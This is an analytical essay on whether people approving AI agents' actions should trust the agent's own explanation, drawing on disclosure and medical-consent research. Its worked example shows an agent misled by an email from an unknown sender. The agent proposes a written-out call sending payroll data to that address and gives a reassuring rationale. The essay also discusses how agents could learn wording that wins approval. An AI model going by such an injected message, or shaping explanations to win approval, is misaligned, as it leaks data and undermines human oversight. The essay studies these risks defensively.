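# Whether humans approving AI actions should rely on the model's own explanation

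## What is an approver asked to decide, and who writes what the approver reads?

An AI agent is an AI system that carries out a task by taking actions, such as running commands, editing files, sending messages or making payments. For example, an agent with access to a user's mailbox can send an email itself, while a chatbot drafts the email and leaves the user to send it. Dhanorkar, Passi and Vorvoreanu (2026), in *Human oversight of agentic systems in practice*, make a similar distinction for programming tools. They count software as an agent if it plans and uses tools by itself to reach the user's goal, but not if it only completes a line of code.

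Many agents stop before a consequential step and show an approval prompt, a short message about the proposed action with a way to allow or deny it. The approver, who answers the prompt, is usually the person who set the task, and so has to get work out of the agent while also supervising it. Mitchell, Ghosh and Passi (2026) write in *AI Agents Push Humans Out of the Loop* that supervision requires expert judgement of each step, some foresight about side effects, and keeping track of the agent's plan and what it has already done. They think current interfaces give little support for any of this.

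With one click, an approver decides both whether an action is harmful and whether the user wanted it, and the answers can differ. Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, interviewed 18 software practitioners and then surveyed 115. One interviewee had given an agent access to a whole workspace so that it could change a single project. The agent also changed other projects, which the permission allowed but the interviewee had not requested. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026) described the job to its participants as "like supervising a new assistant".

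Approvers see little of what led up to a request, so their decisions depend a good deal on the wording of the approval prompt. The agent is the obvious candidate to write that prompt because it is already running, has the details of the task, and writes fluently, but it is also the party asking for permission.

### Why products and laws ask for approval

Some mistakes cannot be undone. Dhanorkar and colleagues mention agents that deleted local files and a Replit agent that erased a database. A developer could try to prohibit such actions for everyone in advance, but users want different things. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026) gives the example of a rule that lets an agent send passport details only to recognised airlines. The rule blocks a user who wants to send them to a specialist travel agency, and it lets the agent share the details of a user who wants nobody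 to have them. Asking each user to decide seems to avoid this problem.

Michael and Roesner reviewed 21 proposed systems for setting an agent's permissions and tried out five commercial agents in May and June 2026. They found researchers and companies moving in different directions. Only three of the 21 proposals rely on asking the user questions while the agent is running to enforce the rules, and over half spare users from specifying permissions directly, for instance by predicting the rules from context. Four of the five commercial agents asked the user questions while running at least some of the time: the Claude chatbot, Claude Cowork (Anthropic's desktop agent), ChatGPT's chat mode and Codex (OpenAI's coding agent). ChatGPT's agent mode, which drives a remote browser, offered no permissions to set and opened a Gmail account without asking.

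An approval prompt may not appear even when the user has asked for one. The Claude chatbot lets users mark each kind of action "Always allow", "Blocked" or "Needs approval". Michael and Roesner selected "Needs approval" for creating email drafts, but Claude created one without asking, and a tag in the browser's log marked the action as not requiring approval. They reproduced this at least three times and reported it to Anthropic. They describe the wider pattern as an "appearance" of control. These products are closed and change quickly, so the details may already be out of date. The survey sorts systems by how users set rules and how software enforces them, but it does not compare the wording that approvers read.

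*Article 14* of the EU's AI Act, in the European Commission's consolidated text, requires providers to design "high-risk" AI systems so that people can oversee them effectively while they are in use. The people overseeing a system must be able to understand what it can and cannot do, spot anomalies, interpret its output correctly, disregard or reverse that output, and stop the system. They must also be able to "remain aware" of automation bias, which the article describes as a tendency to rely automatically, or too much, on the system's output.

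Laux and Ruschemeier (2025), two legal scholars who examine this clause, note that it requires providers to enable awareness of automation bias. This is a modest demand, because an approver can understand automation bias well and still see only the agent's own account on the screen. Article 14 does not prescribe an approval prompt or specify who should write one.

It also does not apply yet. Orrick's *EU AI Act Update* (2026) gives the original date for the main group of high-risk systems as 2 August 2026, but an amending law, the Digital Omnibus, moved it. In the text from the Council of the EU (2026), the duties start on 2 December 2027 for the sensitive uses listed in the Act's Annex III, among them biometrics, critical infrastructure and employment, and on 2 August 2028 for AI in products that other EU safety laws already cover. Many agents will fall outside both groups. The European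 Commission's *How are AI agents addressed within the AI Act?* explains that agents are not a separate category and take on these duties only if they qualify as high-risk. According to the law firm Arthur Cox's summary of the Commission's draft guidelines, that depends on what the provider intends the system for. So Article 14 would probably apply to an agent sold for screening job applicants but not to one sold for tidying an inbox.

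### One action in four forms

In a hypothetical case, an office worker tells an agent, "Send our accountant the March invoices." The agent searches the mailbox and opens a message, from a sender the firm has never dealt with, that gives a new address for the accountant. It then proposes to email that address a spreadsheet containing the invoices and a sheet of payroll data. The approver might see any of the following.

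| Form | What the approver reads |
|---|---|
| Bare command | `send_email(to="d.reyes@reyes-books.example", attachment="finance/march_full.xlsx")` |
| Model-written rationale | "I'm sending the March invoices to your accountant, Dana Reyes, as you asked, so that she can close the month's books." |
| Fixed risk summary | "This action sends a file outside your organisation. You cannot recall a file once it has left. Check the recipient and the attachment." |
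| Record-based summary | "Recipient: d.reyes@reyes-books.example. Earlier messages to this address: none. Source of address: email from an unknown sender, opened by the agent at 09:14. Attachment: march_full.xlsx, sheets 'Invoices' and 'Payroll'." |

The bare command is exact but useless to anyone who does not remember the accountant's real address or what is in the file. The rationale is by far the easiest to read, but it is wrong on the two points that matter. This can happen without any deception by the agent. If it has mistaken the new address for a genuine one, it will write the same sentence it would write if the address were genuine.

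A fixed risk summary is a standard text about a kind of action, written in advance by someone other than the agent. Here the summary is entirely true, but it would be just as true of files that leave the firm properly, so the approver cannot use it alone to tell the bad request from the good ones. It can help only by prompting the approver to look at something else.

The record-based summary, assembled from logged events and exact arguments, does differ between a bad request and a good one. It takes longer to read, and somebody has to choose which records to show, so record-based summaries can differ a lot from one another. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) compared four approval screens. The plainest left out the action's arguments, the policy in force, the history and the consequences. The next added the arguments. The other two, which would both count as record-based,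 contained identical facts, including the policy and the agent's earlier steps, but one listed the steps by time and the other linked them to show their combined effect.

Products can mix the forms, and a screen that shows a rationale above the command seems a natural design. It is then unclear which part the approver uses.

### Independent of the model in what respect?

The texts an approver reads can be independent of the model in who wrote them, what information they were based on, or what incentives their author had. A text can have one kind of independence without the others, so dividing the texts into those that come from the model and those that don't is too coarse.

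Suppose the product uses a second AI model to describe the proposed email. If that model works only from the first agent's account of the task, its description will probably repeat the mistake about the address. Alternatively, the model that proposed the email could write the description from the mail server's log alone. The description would then be based on a sound source, but the model could still leave out the awkward line.

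Incentives are the least clear of the three. A salesperson who writes the risk notice for a product gains from a sale. An agent earns no commission, but its training can have a similar effect. If developers reward finished tasks, and a denial leaves the task unfinished, training will tend to reinforce whatever wording gets approval. How strongly this happens in practice is an empirical question.

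The vendor normally writes the fixed text, and it has incentives too, since it wants customers to keep using the product without too much friction. Vendors also make mistakes. Claude Cowork's prompt for deleting files included a notice about how long the permission would last, which Michael and Roesner found to be inaccurate. After they started a new task, the old one still had the permission when they reopened it. The notice didn't come from the agent or depend on its reasoning. That independence removes some sources of error, but it doesn't guarantee accuracy.

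### From notice to decision

An accurate text can also have no effect. The approver has to notice it, read it, understand it, apply it to the case at hand, and then decide differently because of it. If four in five of the approvers who reached each of these five steps completed it, only about a third of all approvers (0.8⁵ ≈ 0.33) would decide differently.

*Keeping an Eye on AI* (2026) also lists the person's ability to detect the relevant cue as the first condition for successful monitoring. Poor interface design, badly presented cues, too little time, and a lack of attention, motivation or training can all make detection harder.

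Of the 107 practitioners who answered Salerno and colleagues' questions on permission requests, 47.7% said they read the requests carefully, 33.6% said they skim them, and 20.6% said they approve by default. Some look at only one part, with 31.8% checking the file that the request names and 25.2% concentrating on the command or title. Some also skip the agent's own reasoning or stop reading it early, which 42.1% said they sometimes do because of lack of time, tiredness or volume. The respondents were volunteers who work with software for a living, and they were reporting their own habits, where careful reading is the flattering answer. The true figure for careful reading is likely lower, and lower again among people who cannot read a command.

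Understanding is harder to measure. In the survey, 73.0% believed they fully understood what their agents do, but almost half of the interviewees, who had to talk about it at length, described their understanding as partial or absent. When it comes to applying what they read to the case, 67.3% said they are less likely to grant a request that does not fit the task. Whether the request fits the task is the right test for the accountant's email, but the model-written rationale passes it easily because it describes the action in the terms of the task ("the March invoices", "as you asked").

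The chain describes how a text can inform a decision, but a text can also change a decision without informing it. An approver may see a fluent, confident paragraph, take its existence as a sign that things are in order, and click "allow" without checking anything. Mitchell and colleagues cite research in which people took the fluent style of ChatGPT's answers as a sign of accuracy. So evidence that a rationale changed people's decisions is not enough to show that it helped them.

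### Telling persuasion from information

Two rates are needed to see the difference. The legitimate approval rate is the share of harmless, authorised actions that the approver allows. The unsafe approval rate is the share of harmful or unauthorised actions that the approver allows. A good approver has a high legitimate rate and a low unsafe one, and signal detection theory, a standard tool in the psychology of perception, combines the two into a measure of discrimination:

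d′ = z(legitimate approval rate) − z(unsafe approval rate)

Here z converts a proportion into a position on the bell curve, in standard deviations from the middle, so z(50%) is 0, z(75%) is about 0.67, and z(95%) is about 1.64. The formula assumes that the approver forms an impression of how legitimate each request looks and allows everything above some cut-off. Harmless requests look more legitimate on average than harmful ones, but the two groups overlap. The distance between their averages is d′, which is zero for an approver who cannot tell the groups apart.

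An approver who lowers the cut-off will approve more actions, both legitimate and unsafe, but d′ will stay the same. This general readiness to approve is called approval bias. The usual measure is the criterion c, which is minus one half of the sum of the two z values; a lower c means the approver says yes more readily. *Beyond AI advice* (2026) calculates d′ the same way for people who receive AI advice, but replaces the legitimate rate with the rate at which they accept correct advice, and the unsafe rate with the rate at which they accept incorrect advice. Its model assumes that the two groups of impressions are equally spread out, and the formula above needs the same assumption.

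In a hypothetical example, an approver handles 1,000 requests, 10 of which are harmful. Without a rationale, the approver allows 95% of the harmless requests and 50% of the harmful ones. After the product adds a model-written rationale to each prompt, the approver allows 99% of the harmless requests and 75% of the harmful ones.

| | Without rationale | With rationale |
|---|---|---|
| Harmless requests allowed, of 990 | 940.5 | 980.1 |
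| Harmful requests allowed, of 10 | 5 | 7.5 |
| Correct decisions | 94.6% | 98.3% |
| d′ | 1.645 − 0 = 1.645 | 2.326 − 0.674 = 1.652 |

Accuracy has gone up by almost four points, but the approver is no better than before at telling harmful requests from harmless ones (d′ stays near 1.65). The text has only made the approver more biased toward approval, with c falling from −0.82 to −1.50, and a general instruction to relax could have had the same effect.

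Accuracy doesn't show this because harmful requests are rare. An approver who allowed all 1,000 requests without looking would be 99% accurate, better than either column. Now suppose a text did inform the approver, leaving the approval rate for legitimate requests at 95% and cutting the rate for unsafe ones to 25%. That would halve the harmful approvals to 2.5 and raise d′ to about 2.32, yet accuracy would be only 94.8%, well below the figure for the rationale.

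A shift in bias can do more good than harm. In the example, the rationale prevents about 40 wrongful denials but adds 2.5 harmful approvals, which is worthwhile if a harmful approval is less than about 16 times as bad as a wrongful denial. Sending a payroll file to a stranger surely exceeds that threshold. Estimates of d′ are unreliable when a study contains few harmful actions. With ten of them, one changed decision can move the unsafe rate from 50% to 60% and d′ by a quarter of a point.

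In *Same Performance, Hidden Bias*, Benk and Miller (2026) found something close to this pattern. They had 290 people judge whether a given theme was present in sets of 16 words, with or without help from an AI system that was right 70% of the time. People who received a recommendation needed less evidence to say yes than people who worked alone. Their c was lower by 0.19 with a bare recommendation and by 0.34 when an explanation and uncertainty cues came with it. Benk and Miller found no significant difference in d′ between the conditions, but with 290 people split among five groups, the study could have missed one. Judging sets of words is also very different from approving a payment or the deletion of a folder. Still, people who knew more about the task discriminated better, but their knowledge had no effect on where they set the threshold, which is a reason to doubt that expert approvers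 will be immune.

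## Do short standard summaries help consumers choose?

A fixed risk summary applies an old idea, disclosure, to a new kind of decision. Legislators have long required lenders, sellers and doctors to give people a standard text before they sign, hoping to help them choose better. The US Truth in Lending Act, which makes lenders state their interest rates and fees, dates from 1968, so researchers have had decades to study whether disclosures work.

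### The case against mandated disclosure

In *The Failure of Mandated Disclosure* (2010), the American law professors Ben-Shahar and Schneider think short standard summaries mostly don't help consumers choose. They accept that information can help people decide, but doubt that a lawmaker can help by requiring someone else to provide a standard text. For that to work, the lawmaker has to choose the right facts, the firm has to present them properly even when it would rather not, and the reader has to do the rest.

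Most of their argument concerns the reader. They later expanded it into a book, *More Than You Wanted to Know*. The law professor Ryan Bubb summarises and criticises the book in his review, *TMI?* (Bubb, 2015). The book starts with the number of disclosures, counting 49 separate documents at a typical US mortgage closing. Each new one takes attention from the rest, so people skip them, which the book treats as sensible. Even the judge Richard Posner admitted to signing home loan papers without reading them. People who do read disclosures often lack the literacy, numeracy or background knowledge to use what they find.

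Ben-Shahar and Schneider also reject shorter, simpler texts as a remedy, because "the complex isn't simple and can't easily be made so". Their example is the annual percentage rate (APR), a single figure for the yearly cost of a loan. An APR lets a borrower compare two similar loans, but it isn't enough to choose between a cheaper loan with a penalty for early repayment and a more expensive loan without one. They add that short forms get longer because lawmakers keep finding more to include.

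The point about simplifying matters most for approval prompts, which are already short, but it is also the weakest part of the argument. A short text can't contain everything relevant to a mortgage, but it might still help if it contains the one thing the borrower would otherwise miss. Whether it does needs to be tested.

### Do people read and understand the short version?

Ben-Shahar ran such a test with Adam Chilton, a colleague at the University of Chicago. For *Simplification of Privacy Disclosures* (2016), they had a market research firm survey people about risky sexual behaviour and randomly varied the privacy notice shown first. The University of Chicago Law School's *Bringing Data to the Privacy Debate* describes the set-up. The survey was presented as part of an effort to develop treatments for sexually transmitted diseases. Respondents saw one of six versions of the same policy,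 which ranged from following all of the usual advice on clear writing (plain titles, concrete examples, active language, good organisation, readable type) to following none of it. The simplifications tested included a warning box listing the practices people would least expect. A control group saw a blank screen.

The policy was alarming, because the researchers told people that they would sell the data, give it to insurance companies and leave it unsecured. Yet simplifying the notice had little or no effect on how well respondents understood it, how much they disclosed about themselves, or what rights they expected to have. Respondents who saw the notice were happy with the policy, and so was the group that saw a blank screen.

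Ben-Shahar had already argued in print that such notices are useless, so he and Chilton circulated a draft of the paper before collecting the data, which makes it harder to suspect them of picking the result afterwards. The experiment covered the steps from reading a notice to making a decision. Even comprehension didn't improve, so the notices probably failed at an early step. Someone clicking through a survey has little reason to read a privacy notice in any format. Ben-Shahar (2017) nevertheless told Congress that simplified privacy disclosures "will have no effect" on the behaviour of consumers or of the companies collecting their data. One survey seems too little evidence for that claim, particularly about the companies, whose behaviour the experiment didn't observe.

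People who have a reason to read can learn a lot from a short text. The Behavioural Insights Team's *Improving consumer comprehension of online contractual terms and privacy policies* (2019) describes six online experiments for the UK government, with 7,953 participants. In the first, 1,812 people looked at a checkout page for a T-shirt and then answered eight questions about the shop's terms. People who saw only a link to the terms got about 3.4 questions right. Putting the full terms in a scrollable box on the page raised the score by 26.3%. Showing four key terms with icons raised it by 33.9%, and showing four as questions and answers raised it by 36.0%.

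Nearly all of the gain from the summaries was on the terms they covered, where scores were 80.7% higher than with the link. On the other terms, the scrollable box raised scores the most, by 14.8%, compared with 7.7% for the questions and answers. So a summary's author largely determines what readers learn, although in this case no group learned less about the omitted terms than the people who only had the link. None of the versions significantly changed how much people trusted the shop or wanted to buy from it. The team had modelled the terms on those of real retailers, and they may have contained no good reason not to buy.

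These participants knew that questions were coming and earned about 10p for each correct answer. The experiment therefore shows what people can understand when they pay attention, which Ben-Shahar and Chilton's respondents seem not to have done. Asking approvers whether they read doesn't settle which group they resemble. In *Putting Disclosures to the Test* (2016), a staff summary of a US Federal Trade Commission workshop, Mariea Grubbs Hoy describes a study of the risk notice in an advertisement for allergy medicine. Eighty percent of participants said they had read at least half of the notice, but eye tracking showed that most hadn't. This adds to the doubt about how many of Salerno and colleagues' practitioners read permission requests carefully.

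The most thorough test of understanding comes from mortgages. For *Improving Consumer Mortgage Disclosures* (2007), Lacko and Pappalardo, two economists at the Federal Trade Commission, designed a three-page loan form to replace the existing ones, with all the key costs on the first page. They gave 819 recent borrowers either the old forms or the new one for two hypothetical loans and asked about the terms. The average score was 61% with the old forms and 80% with the new one. *Improving Mortgage Disclosures* (Lacko and Pappalardo 2008) explains that respondents could keep looking at the forms while they answered, so the scores depended on understanding and hardly at all on attention or memory.

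The detailed results suggest that complex things can be made simple. The new form helped more with a complicated loan (56% to 78%) than with a plain one (66% to 82%). It helped most with the total of the up-front charges, which the existing rules didn't require forms to show. With the old forms, 87% of people failed to identify that total, and the new form cut this by 66 percentage points. But 30% still overlooked a large final payment, the same share as with the old forms. The question closest to an actual choice was which of the two loans was cheaper, and the share who got it wrong fell only from 37% to 24%.

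Standard forms can also mislead. In 36 interviews before the test, Lacko and Pappalardo found that many borrowers thought the "discount fee" on the official form was a discount they had received, when it was a fee they had paid.

### Does understanding change the choice?

In *How Does Simplified Disclosure Affect Individuals' Mutual Fund Choices?* (2011), Beshears, Choi and colleagues gave 186 Harvard staff members two imaginary portfolios of $100,000 to invest, one in stock funds and one in bond funds. A third of the participants received each fund's full prospectus, which can run to hundreds of pages. Another third received a summary of two to four pages, and the rest received the summary and could ask for the full version, though few did. The researchers paid participants about $100 on average, depending on the actual returns of one of their portfolios.

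The summary did not significantly change the fees people paid or the past returns of the funds they chose, even though many participants could have chosen better. Many of the funds charged a "load", a one-off sales fee, and half of the participants had to hold their funds for only a month. To make up for a 2% load in that time, a fund would have to outperform a fund without one by about 2% (1/0.98 ≈ 1.02), which compounds to about 27% over a year. Avoiding loads was therefore the only sensible strategy, yet participants with the one-month horizon paid 3% on average, two percentage points above the lowest available. Judging by the standard errors, the summary is unlikely to have cut their total fees by more than about 0.3 points, so the study was large enough to rule out most of the possible improvement.

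Participants had the documents in front of them and spent over 20 minutes on the task, so they didn't fail to notice the information. Beshears and colleagues conclude that people either didn't understand loads or didn't take them into account when choosing. People who got the summary took 22.5 minutes instead of 31.2 and made choices that were no worse. Someone who has to approve an agent's actions all day might well value the time saved.

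Sometimes an accurate text makes a consumer's choice worse. Mercer and Taha (2015), in *Unintended Consequences*, studied mail-in rebates, where the buyer pays full price and then posts a form to get some of it back. Most people never post the form, and legal scholars had proposed that sellers disclose this. Mercer and Taha showed 549 US consumers advertisements for two DVD players, a Panasonic at $169.99 and a slightly inferior Sony at $179.99. The share choosing the Sony was 25% at full price and 46% with a $40 rebate.

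The share of participants choosing the Sony rose to 55% when the advertisement disclosed that buyers redeem about 30% of such rebates. It was 59% with a note that people overestimate their chances of redeeming because they forget, procrastinate or lose the paperwork, and 72% with both notes. Participants had evidently seen the small print, since only 21% chose the Sony when a notice in the same spot said it was refurbished.

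Mercer and Taha think that readers took the warning to be about other people, and that some may have resented being told what not to do. Their direct evidence of increased optimism is less convincing than it looks, because they measured optimism by how much higher people rated their own chances of redeeming than other buyers' chances. Telling people that few buyers redeem should lower their estimate for others, so the gap can widen even if nobody becomes more confident. The choices people made don't have this problem, but they were hypothetical, and each version had fewer than 80 people on average. These readers seem to have understood the fact but failed to apply it to themselves.

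Disclosures can make it harder for consumers to compare loans. In 2002, the US housing department proposed that mortgage brokers disclose any extra payment they receive from a lender for arranging a loan at a higher interest rate. In *The Effect of Mortgage Broker Compensation Disclosures on Consumers and Competition*, Lacko and Pappalardo (2004) showed about 500 recent borrowers the costs of two loans. Around 90% could identify the cheaper loan without the disclosure, compared with 63–72% with it, depending on the wording. The share who would choose the cheaper loan fell from 85–94% to 60–70%. When both loans cost the same, about half of the respondents who saw the disclosure failed to recognise this, and most of them thought the loan with the disclosure was more expensive.

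Respondents mistook a true figure for an extra cost. The disclosure concerned a conflict of interest, but distrust of brokers can't easily explain the result, because the researchers never told respondents which loan came from a broker. In an abstract posted in Public Citizen's *Bambauer et al. Article on Defects in Privacy Disclosures*, Bambauer and colleagues count a disclosure as valuable only if it points to something that matters without causing an overreaction, a test this disclosure failed.

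The best evidence that a short text can change real behaviour comes from payday loans, small loans that fall due on the borrower's next payday. For *Information Disclosure, Cognitive Biases and Payday Borrowing* (2009), Bertrand and Morse persuaded a large US lender to try handing over the cash in new envelopes at 77 shops. One version compared the dollar cost of a $300 payday loan with the cost of the same debt on a credit card. The payday loan cost $45 for two weeks and $270 for three months, compared with $2.50 and $15 on the card. Another version compared annual interest rates, and a third showed how long borrowers typically take to repay. The researchers assigned the versions at random to shops and days.

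Over the next four months, people who had received the dollar comparison were 5.9 percentage points less likely to borrow in a given pay cycle, a fall of 11%. They also borrowed 23% less money. The amount borrowed fell less among people shown interest rates (16%) or repayment times (12%), and a savings planner included in some envelopes had no effect. Bertrand and Morse took these figures from the lender's records, so the results reflect real borrowing decisions.

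Credit Slips' *Disclosure 2.5* (2013), a blog post, objects that the lender's behaviour stayed fixed during the experiment. A lender who has to print an unwelcome message every day may find ways round it. A rough test of this came in January 2012, when Texas began requiring a similar disclosure across the state. Wang and Burke, in *The Effects of Disclosure and Enforcement on Payday Lending in Texas*, attribute a 13% fall in loan volume over the first six months to the requirement. Texas didn't randomise the disclosure, and Austin and Dallas tightened their own rules at the same time, but the fall is encouragingly close to the experimental result.

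### Influence without information

People may borrow less without making better decisions about borrowing. Some people who stopped may have been heading for months of fees, while others may have needed the money for a car repair and had nowhere else to get it. Neither payday study shows how many people were in each group. In the terms used for approvers, the envelopes may have improved discrimination or only made everyone more likely to say no.

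In his review, Bubb separates two ways a disclosure can work, using a distinction from psychology between slow, deliberate thinking ("System 2") and fast, automatic thinking ("System 1"). He agrees with Ben-Shahar and Schneider that texts meant for deliberate thinking often fail because people seldom deliberate. But a disclosure can also act on fast thinking, and then their main objection doesn't apply. When Starbucks posted calorie counts, average calories per purchase fell by 6%. Surveys found no significant improvement in customers' knowledge of the counts, but more customers mentioned calories or health as a reason for their choice.

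This kind of influence affects people who were right as well as people who were wrong. Bubb shows this with the graphic cigarette labels that US regulators planned in 2011. About half of smokers die of a smoking-related illness, and in survey data 41.5% of smokers guessed too low. A picture that raises everyone's estimate a little moves those smokers towards the truth and the other 58.5% away from it. That may be acceptable for tobacco, where the aim is to reduce smoking. It would work badly for an AI agent's actions, because a frightening standard text on every outgoing email would lead approvers to reject good emails too.

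Bubb rejects Ben-Shahar and Schneider's conclusion that lawmakers should give up on disclosure, and calls for testing each text. The results above support him, because some texts clearly worked and others clearly failed, and nobody could have reliably told which were which by reading them.

### One concrete cost, at the moment of choosing?

There is only weak support for the idea that disclosures work when they give one concrete cost, tied to the choice, at the moment of choosing. The dollar figures on the payday envelope and the total on the new mortgage form do seem to fit this idea, while a privacy policy or a prospectus contains too much information.

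| Text | One concrete figure or fact? | Shown at the choice? | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Payday fees in dollars | Nearly: one cost over several periods | No, after the loan | Less borrowing later |
| New mortgage form | No, a dozen costs | Yes, in a simulation | Much better understanding |
| "Refurbished" notice | Yes, but not a cost | Yes | Fewer chose the product |
| Rebate redemption rate | Yes | Yes | More chose the rebate |
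| Broker's payment | Yes | Yes | More chose the dearer loan |
| Short fund prospectus | No, many items | Yes | Same choices, less time |

Two cases complicate the question of when to show a summary. Borrowers got the payday envelope after the lender had approved the loan, so it could mainly affect their next one. The Federal Trade Commission's workshop summary describes two experiments with a quiz app, in which Rebecca Balebako found that people who saw a privacy notice before downloading the app later answered fewer questions about the notice correctly than people who saw it after installing. The experiments measured memory and not choice, but they suggest that people are less attentive when they are about to get something they want.

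The number of facts shown also doesn't explain why some disclosures helped and others didn't. The rebate rate and the broker's payment were each a single figure shown at the right moment, and both disclosures backfired.

The successful disclosures left readers little to work out. "Refurbished" described the specific DVD player on offer, and everyone knows it counts against the player. The payday envelope had already added up the fees, and the mortgage form had totalled the charges. By contrast, the rebate rate described buyers in general, and each reader had to accept being one of them. The broker's payment made sense only to readers who knew how it related to the total cost, and they had to weigh a load against the length of the investment.

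This explanation does not easily account for Ben-Shahar and Chilton's survey, where plain statements about the survey itself had no effect. Perhaps nobody read them, but another experiment in the Chicago account suggests that reading might not have helped. Lior Strahilevitz and Matthew Kugler showed 1,441 Americans either vague or explicit excerpts from Facebook's and Google's privacy policies. The wording made no measurable difference, despite evidence that people read closely. Many found the practices highly intrusive but believed they had agreed to them, even after reading the vague version. A specific, easily understood fact may not matter to someone who already assumes the worst or sees no alternative. The explanation was also devised after the results were known, and from only a handful of studies, so it is only a hypothesis for approval screens.

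If this is right, it counts against fixed risk summaries. In the accountant's invoices example, "This action sends a file outside your organisation" resembles the rebate rate, while "Earlier messages to this address: none" is more like the refurbished notice.

### How far approving resembles buying

Consumers choose for themselves, and usually only they know what they want, so many of these studies measure understanding or use artificial cases in which one option is plainly cheaper. An approver judges an action that an agent has chosen, and whether that action was authorised is often a matter of fact. This should make good approvals easier to define and score. But an approver usually sees one proposal and can only accept it or delay the work, whereas a shopper can compare two loans side by side.

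Repetition may be the bigger difference. Few people take out more than a handful of mortgages, but an approver may answer dozens of prompts in a day, and a notice that works the first time may go unnoticed by the thirtieth. Payday borrowers do return for more loans, but Bertrand and Morse's envelopes were used for only two weeks.

In *Clear Disclosures*, Bucher, Caplin and colleagues (2024) use a task closer to the approver's job. Participants accept or reject privacy policies over 30 rounds, reading versions of either about 1,300 words or about 250. Each participant has five "red flags" to look for, and accepting is correct only if the policy contains no more than two of them. Each flag has a 50% chance of appearing, so someone who accepts every policy unread will be right half the time. Approvers rarely see harmful requests, so accepting unread is usually right for them and they have far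 less reason to read.

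## Do risk summaries help patients understand and decide?

Signing a medical consent form is more like approving an agent's action than shopping is. Someone else has proposed the action, the patient can usually only agree or refuse, and a mistake can do lasting harm. Patients also have a much better reason to read than someone clicking past a privacy notice, and a doctor or nurse normally talks them through the form. These conditions should make patients more likely than most readers to learn from a standard text.

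### What people know after they sign

*Participants' understanding of informed consent in clinical trials over three decades* (Tam, Huy and colleagues, 2015) pooled 103 studies that questioned clinical trial participants, or parents who had consented for a child.

| What the person had to understand | Share who did | 95% confidence interval |
|---|---|---|
| They could withdraw at any time | 75.8% | 70.6–80.3 |
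| The purpose of the study | 69.6% | 63.5–75.1 |
| The risks and side effects | 67.0% | 57.4–75.4 |
| At least one risk, by name | 54.9% | 43.3–65.0 |
| Randomisation | 52.1% | 41.3–62.7 |

Only about half of the participants knew that randomisation means chance decides which treatment a patient gets. Different studies covered different items, so small gaps between the rows mean little. The gap between knowing about risks and naming one probably comes from how the questions were asked. Picking an answer from a list is easier than producing one, and Tam and colleagues also found lower understanding of the study's purpose and the right to withdraw where researchers had asked open questions.

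Understanding of these items did not improve over 30 years. Tam and colleagues suggest that trials may have become more complicated, or that researchers put too little effort into consent, but they admit that their analysis may have been too weak to detect an improvement. PLoS ONE published an updated meta-analysis by another team in 2024 but retracted it the following year (*Retraction*, 2025).

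The averages also hide large differences. *The reality of informed consent* (Pietrzykowski and Smilowska, 2021) reviewed 14 studies, in which the share of people who understood randomisation ranged from 10% to 96%, and the share who understood the risks ranged from 7% to 100%. The 100% came from a group who could look up the answers in the consent form.

People are poor judges of their own understanding. In an Argentine study that Pietrzykowski and Smilowska describe, 51.4% of patients rated their knowledge of the trial as high, but only 14.3% showed a high level when tested. *Consent to research participation*, a study of German school pupils, found that 87% thought a consent form was easy or very easy to understand. But only 33% knew they would not benefit personally from taking part, and 58% believed the study medicine would help them get better.

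This pattern plausibly arises because people expect doctors to choose the treatment that suits them and expect medicines to help. Randomisation and the lack of personal benefit contradict those expectations, while the right to say no fits what most people already believe. An approver who expects the agent to follow its instructions may have the same trouble understanding a detail that suggests otherwise.

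### Shorter forms and "key information"

*A randomized control trial of re-designed and shorter research informed consent forms* (Emanuel, Lopez-Rico and colleagues, 2026) compared three versions of the consent form from a real trial of a stroke drug. The original was 21 pages long. The researchers wrote a 14-page version with simpler words, risk tables and timelines, and a three-page version based on a summary template that the US Food and Drug Administration (FDA) drafted in 2024. Each of 334 US adults read one version and then answered 14 questions without being able to look back at it.

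| | 21 pages | 14 pages | 3 pages |
|---|---|---|---|
| Estimated reading time | 31 minutes | 18 minutes | 6 minutes |
| Average score | 65.7% | 79.3% | 69.3% |
| Named the drug's most common risk | 31.1% | 68.2% | 57.3% |
| Felt well informed | 93.2% | 96.2% | 95.9% |

The 14-page form did best, but it differed from the original in length, wording and layout, so the trial can't show which of these helped. The three-page form used equally plain language, so it probably scored lower because of what it left out. Similarly, the Behavioural Insights Team's shop summaries mainly taught people about the terms they covered.

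The result for the three-page form is more relevant to approvers, who won't read 14 pages. With that form, people scored about as well as with the original in a fifth of the reading time, and nearly twice as many could name the main risk. But they were healthy volunteers imagining themselves as patients, and real patients might read either form more closely.

*A randomized trial comparing concise and standard consent forms* (2017), the largest randomised study of consent forms at the time, found that comprehension and satisfaction did not vary with the form's length or complexity in a real trial about when to start HIV treatment. Emanuel and colleagues argue that simple forms are hard to test inside real trials because ethics boards insist on adding their own standard language. In earlier studies, these additions averaged 463 words and were written for readers with 11 years of schooling.

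The 2018 revision of the Common Rule, the US federal policy on research with human subjects, keeps the long consent form but requires it to begin with a "concise and focused" presentation of the key information that would help someone decide whether to take part. According to *Characterization of key information sections in informed consent forms posted on ClinicalTrials.gov*, this requirement applies to trials that began on or after 21 January 2019, and the rule does not list what the section must contain.

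The federal Office for Human Research Protections recommends that a key information section cover the right to refuse or stop, the purpose, duration, procedures, risks, benefits, alternatives, and any payment or costs, according to *Qualitative assessment of proposed visual key information pages for informed consent*. That is most of a consent form, which lends some support to Ben-Shahar and Schneider's complaint that short forms tend to grow. Evidence-based advice on how to use these sections is still limited, according to *Assessing the Usability of a Novel Toolkit* (2025). Emanuel and colleagues say that people who get a summary in front of a standard form routinely ignore the form. People approving AI actions could likewise ignore the exact command if the screen shows a summary above it.

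*Experimenting with modifications to consent forms in comparative effectiveness research* (Niyibizi, Speight and colleagues, 2022) reports an online experiment with 753 people. Participants imagined that a relative had bleeding around the brain and could not make decisions, then chose whether the relative should join a trial comparing two standard fluids. One group's consent form opened with a standard key information page, and another's opened with a simpler, more positive one. A third group got the simpler page plus a line saying that taking part involved no extra costs.

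Of those who saw the standard page, 44% understood that a computer would assign the treatment at random, while 47% thought a doctor would choose whatever was best for the patient. The share who understood the random assignment was 59% with the simpler page and 46% with the simpler page plus the line on costs.

This improvement looks fragile. Most of it disappeared when the researchers added a line about costs, which has no obvious bearing on randomisation. In an earlier experiment by the same team, 68% of a different online group understood randomisation after reading the form that produced the 44%. The gap between the two groups of readers was therefore larger than the gap between the forms.

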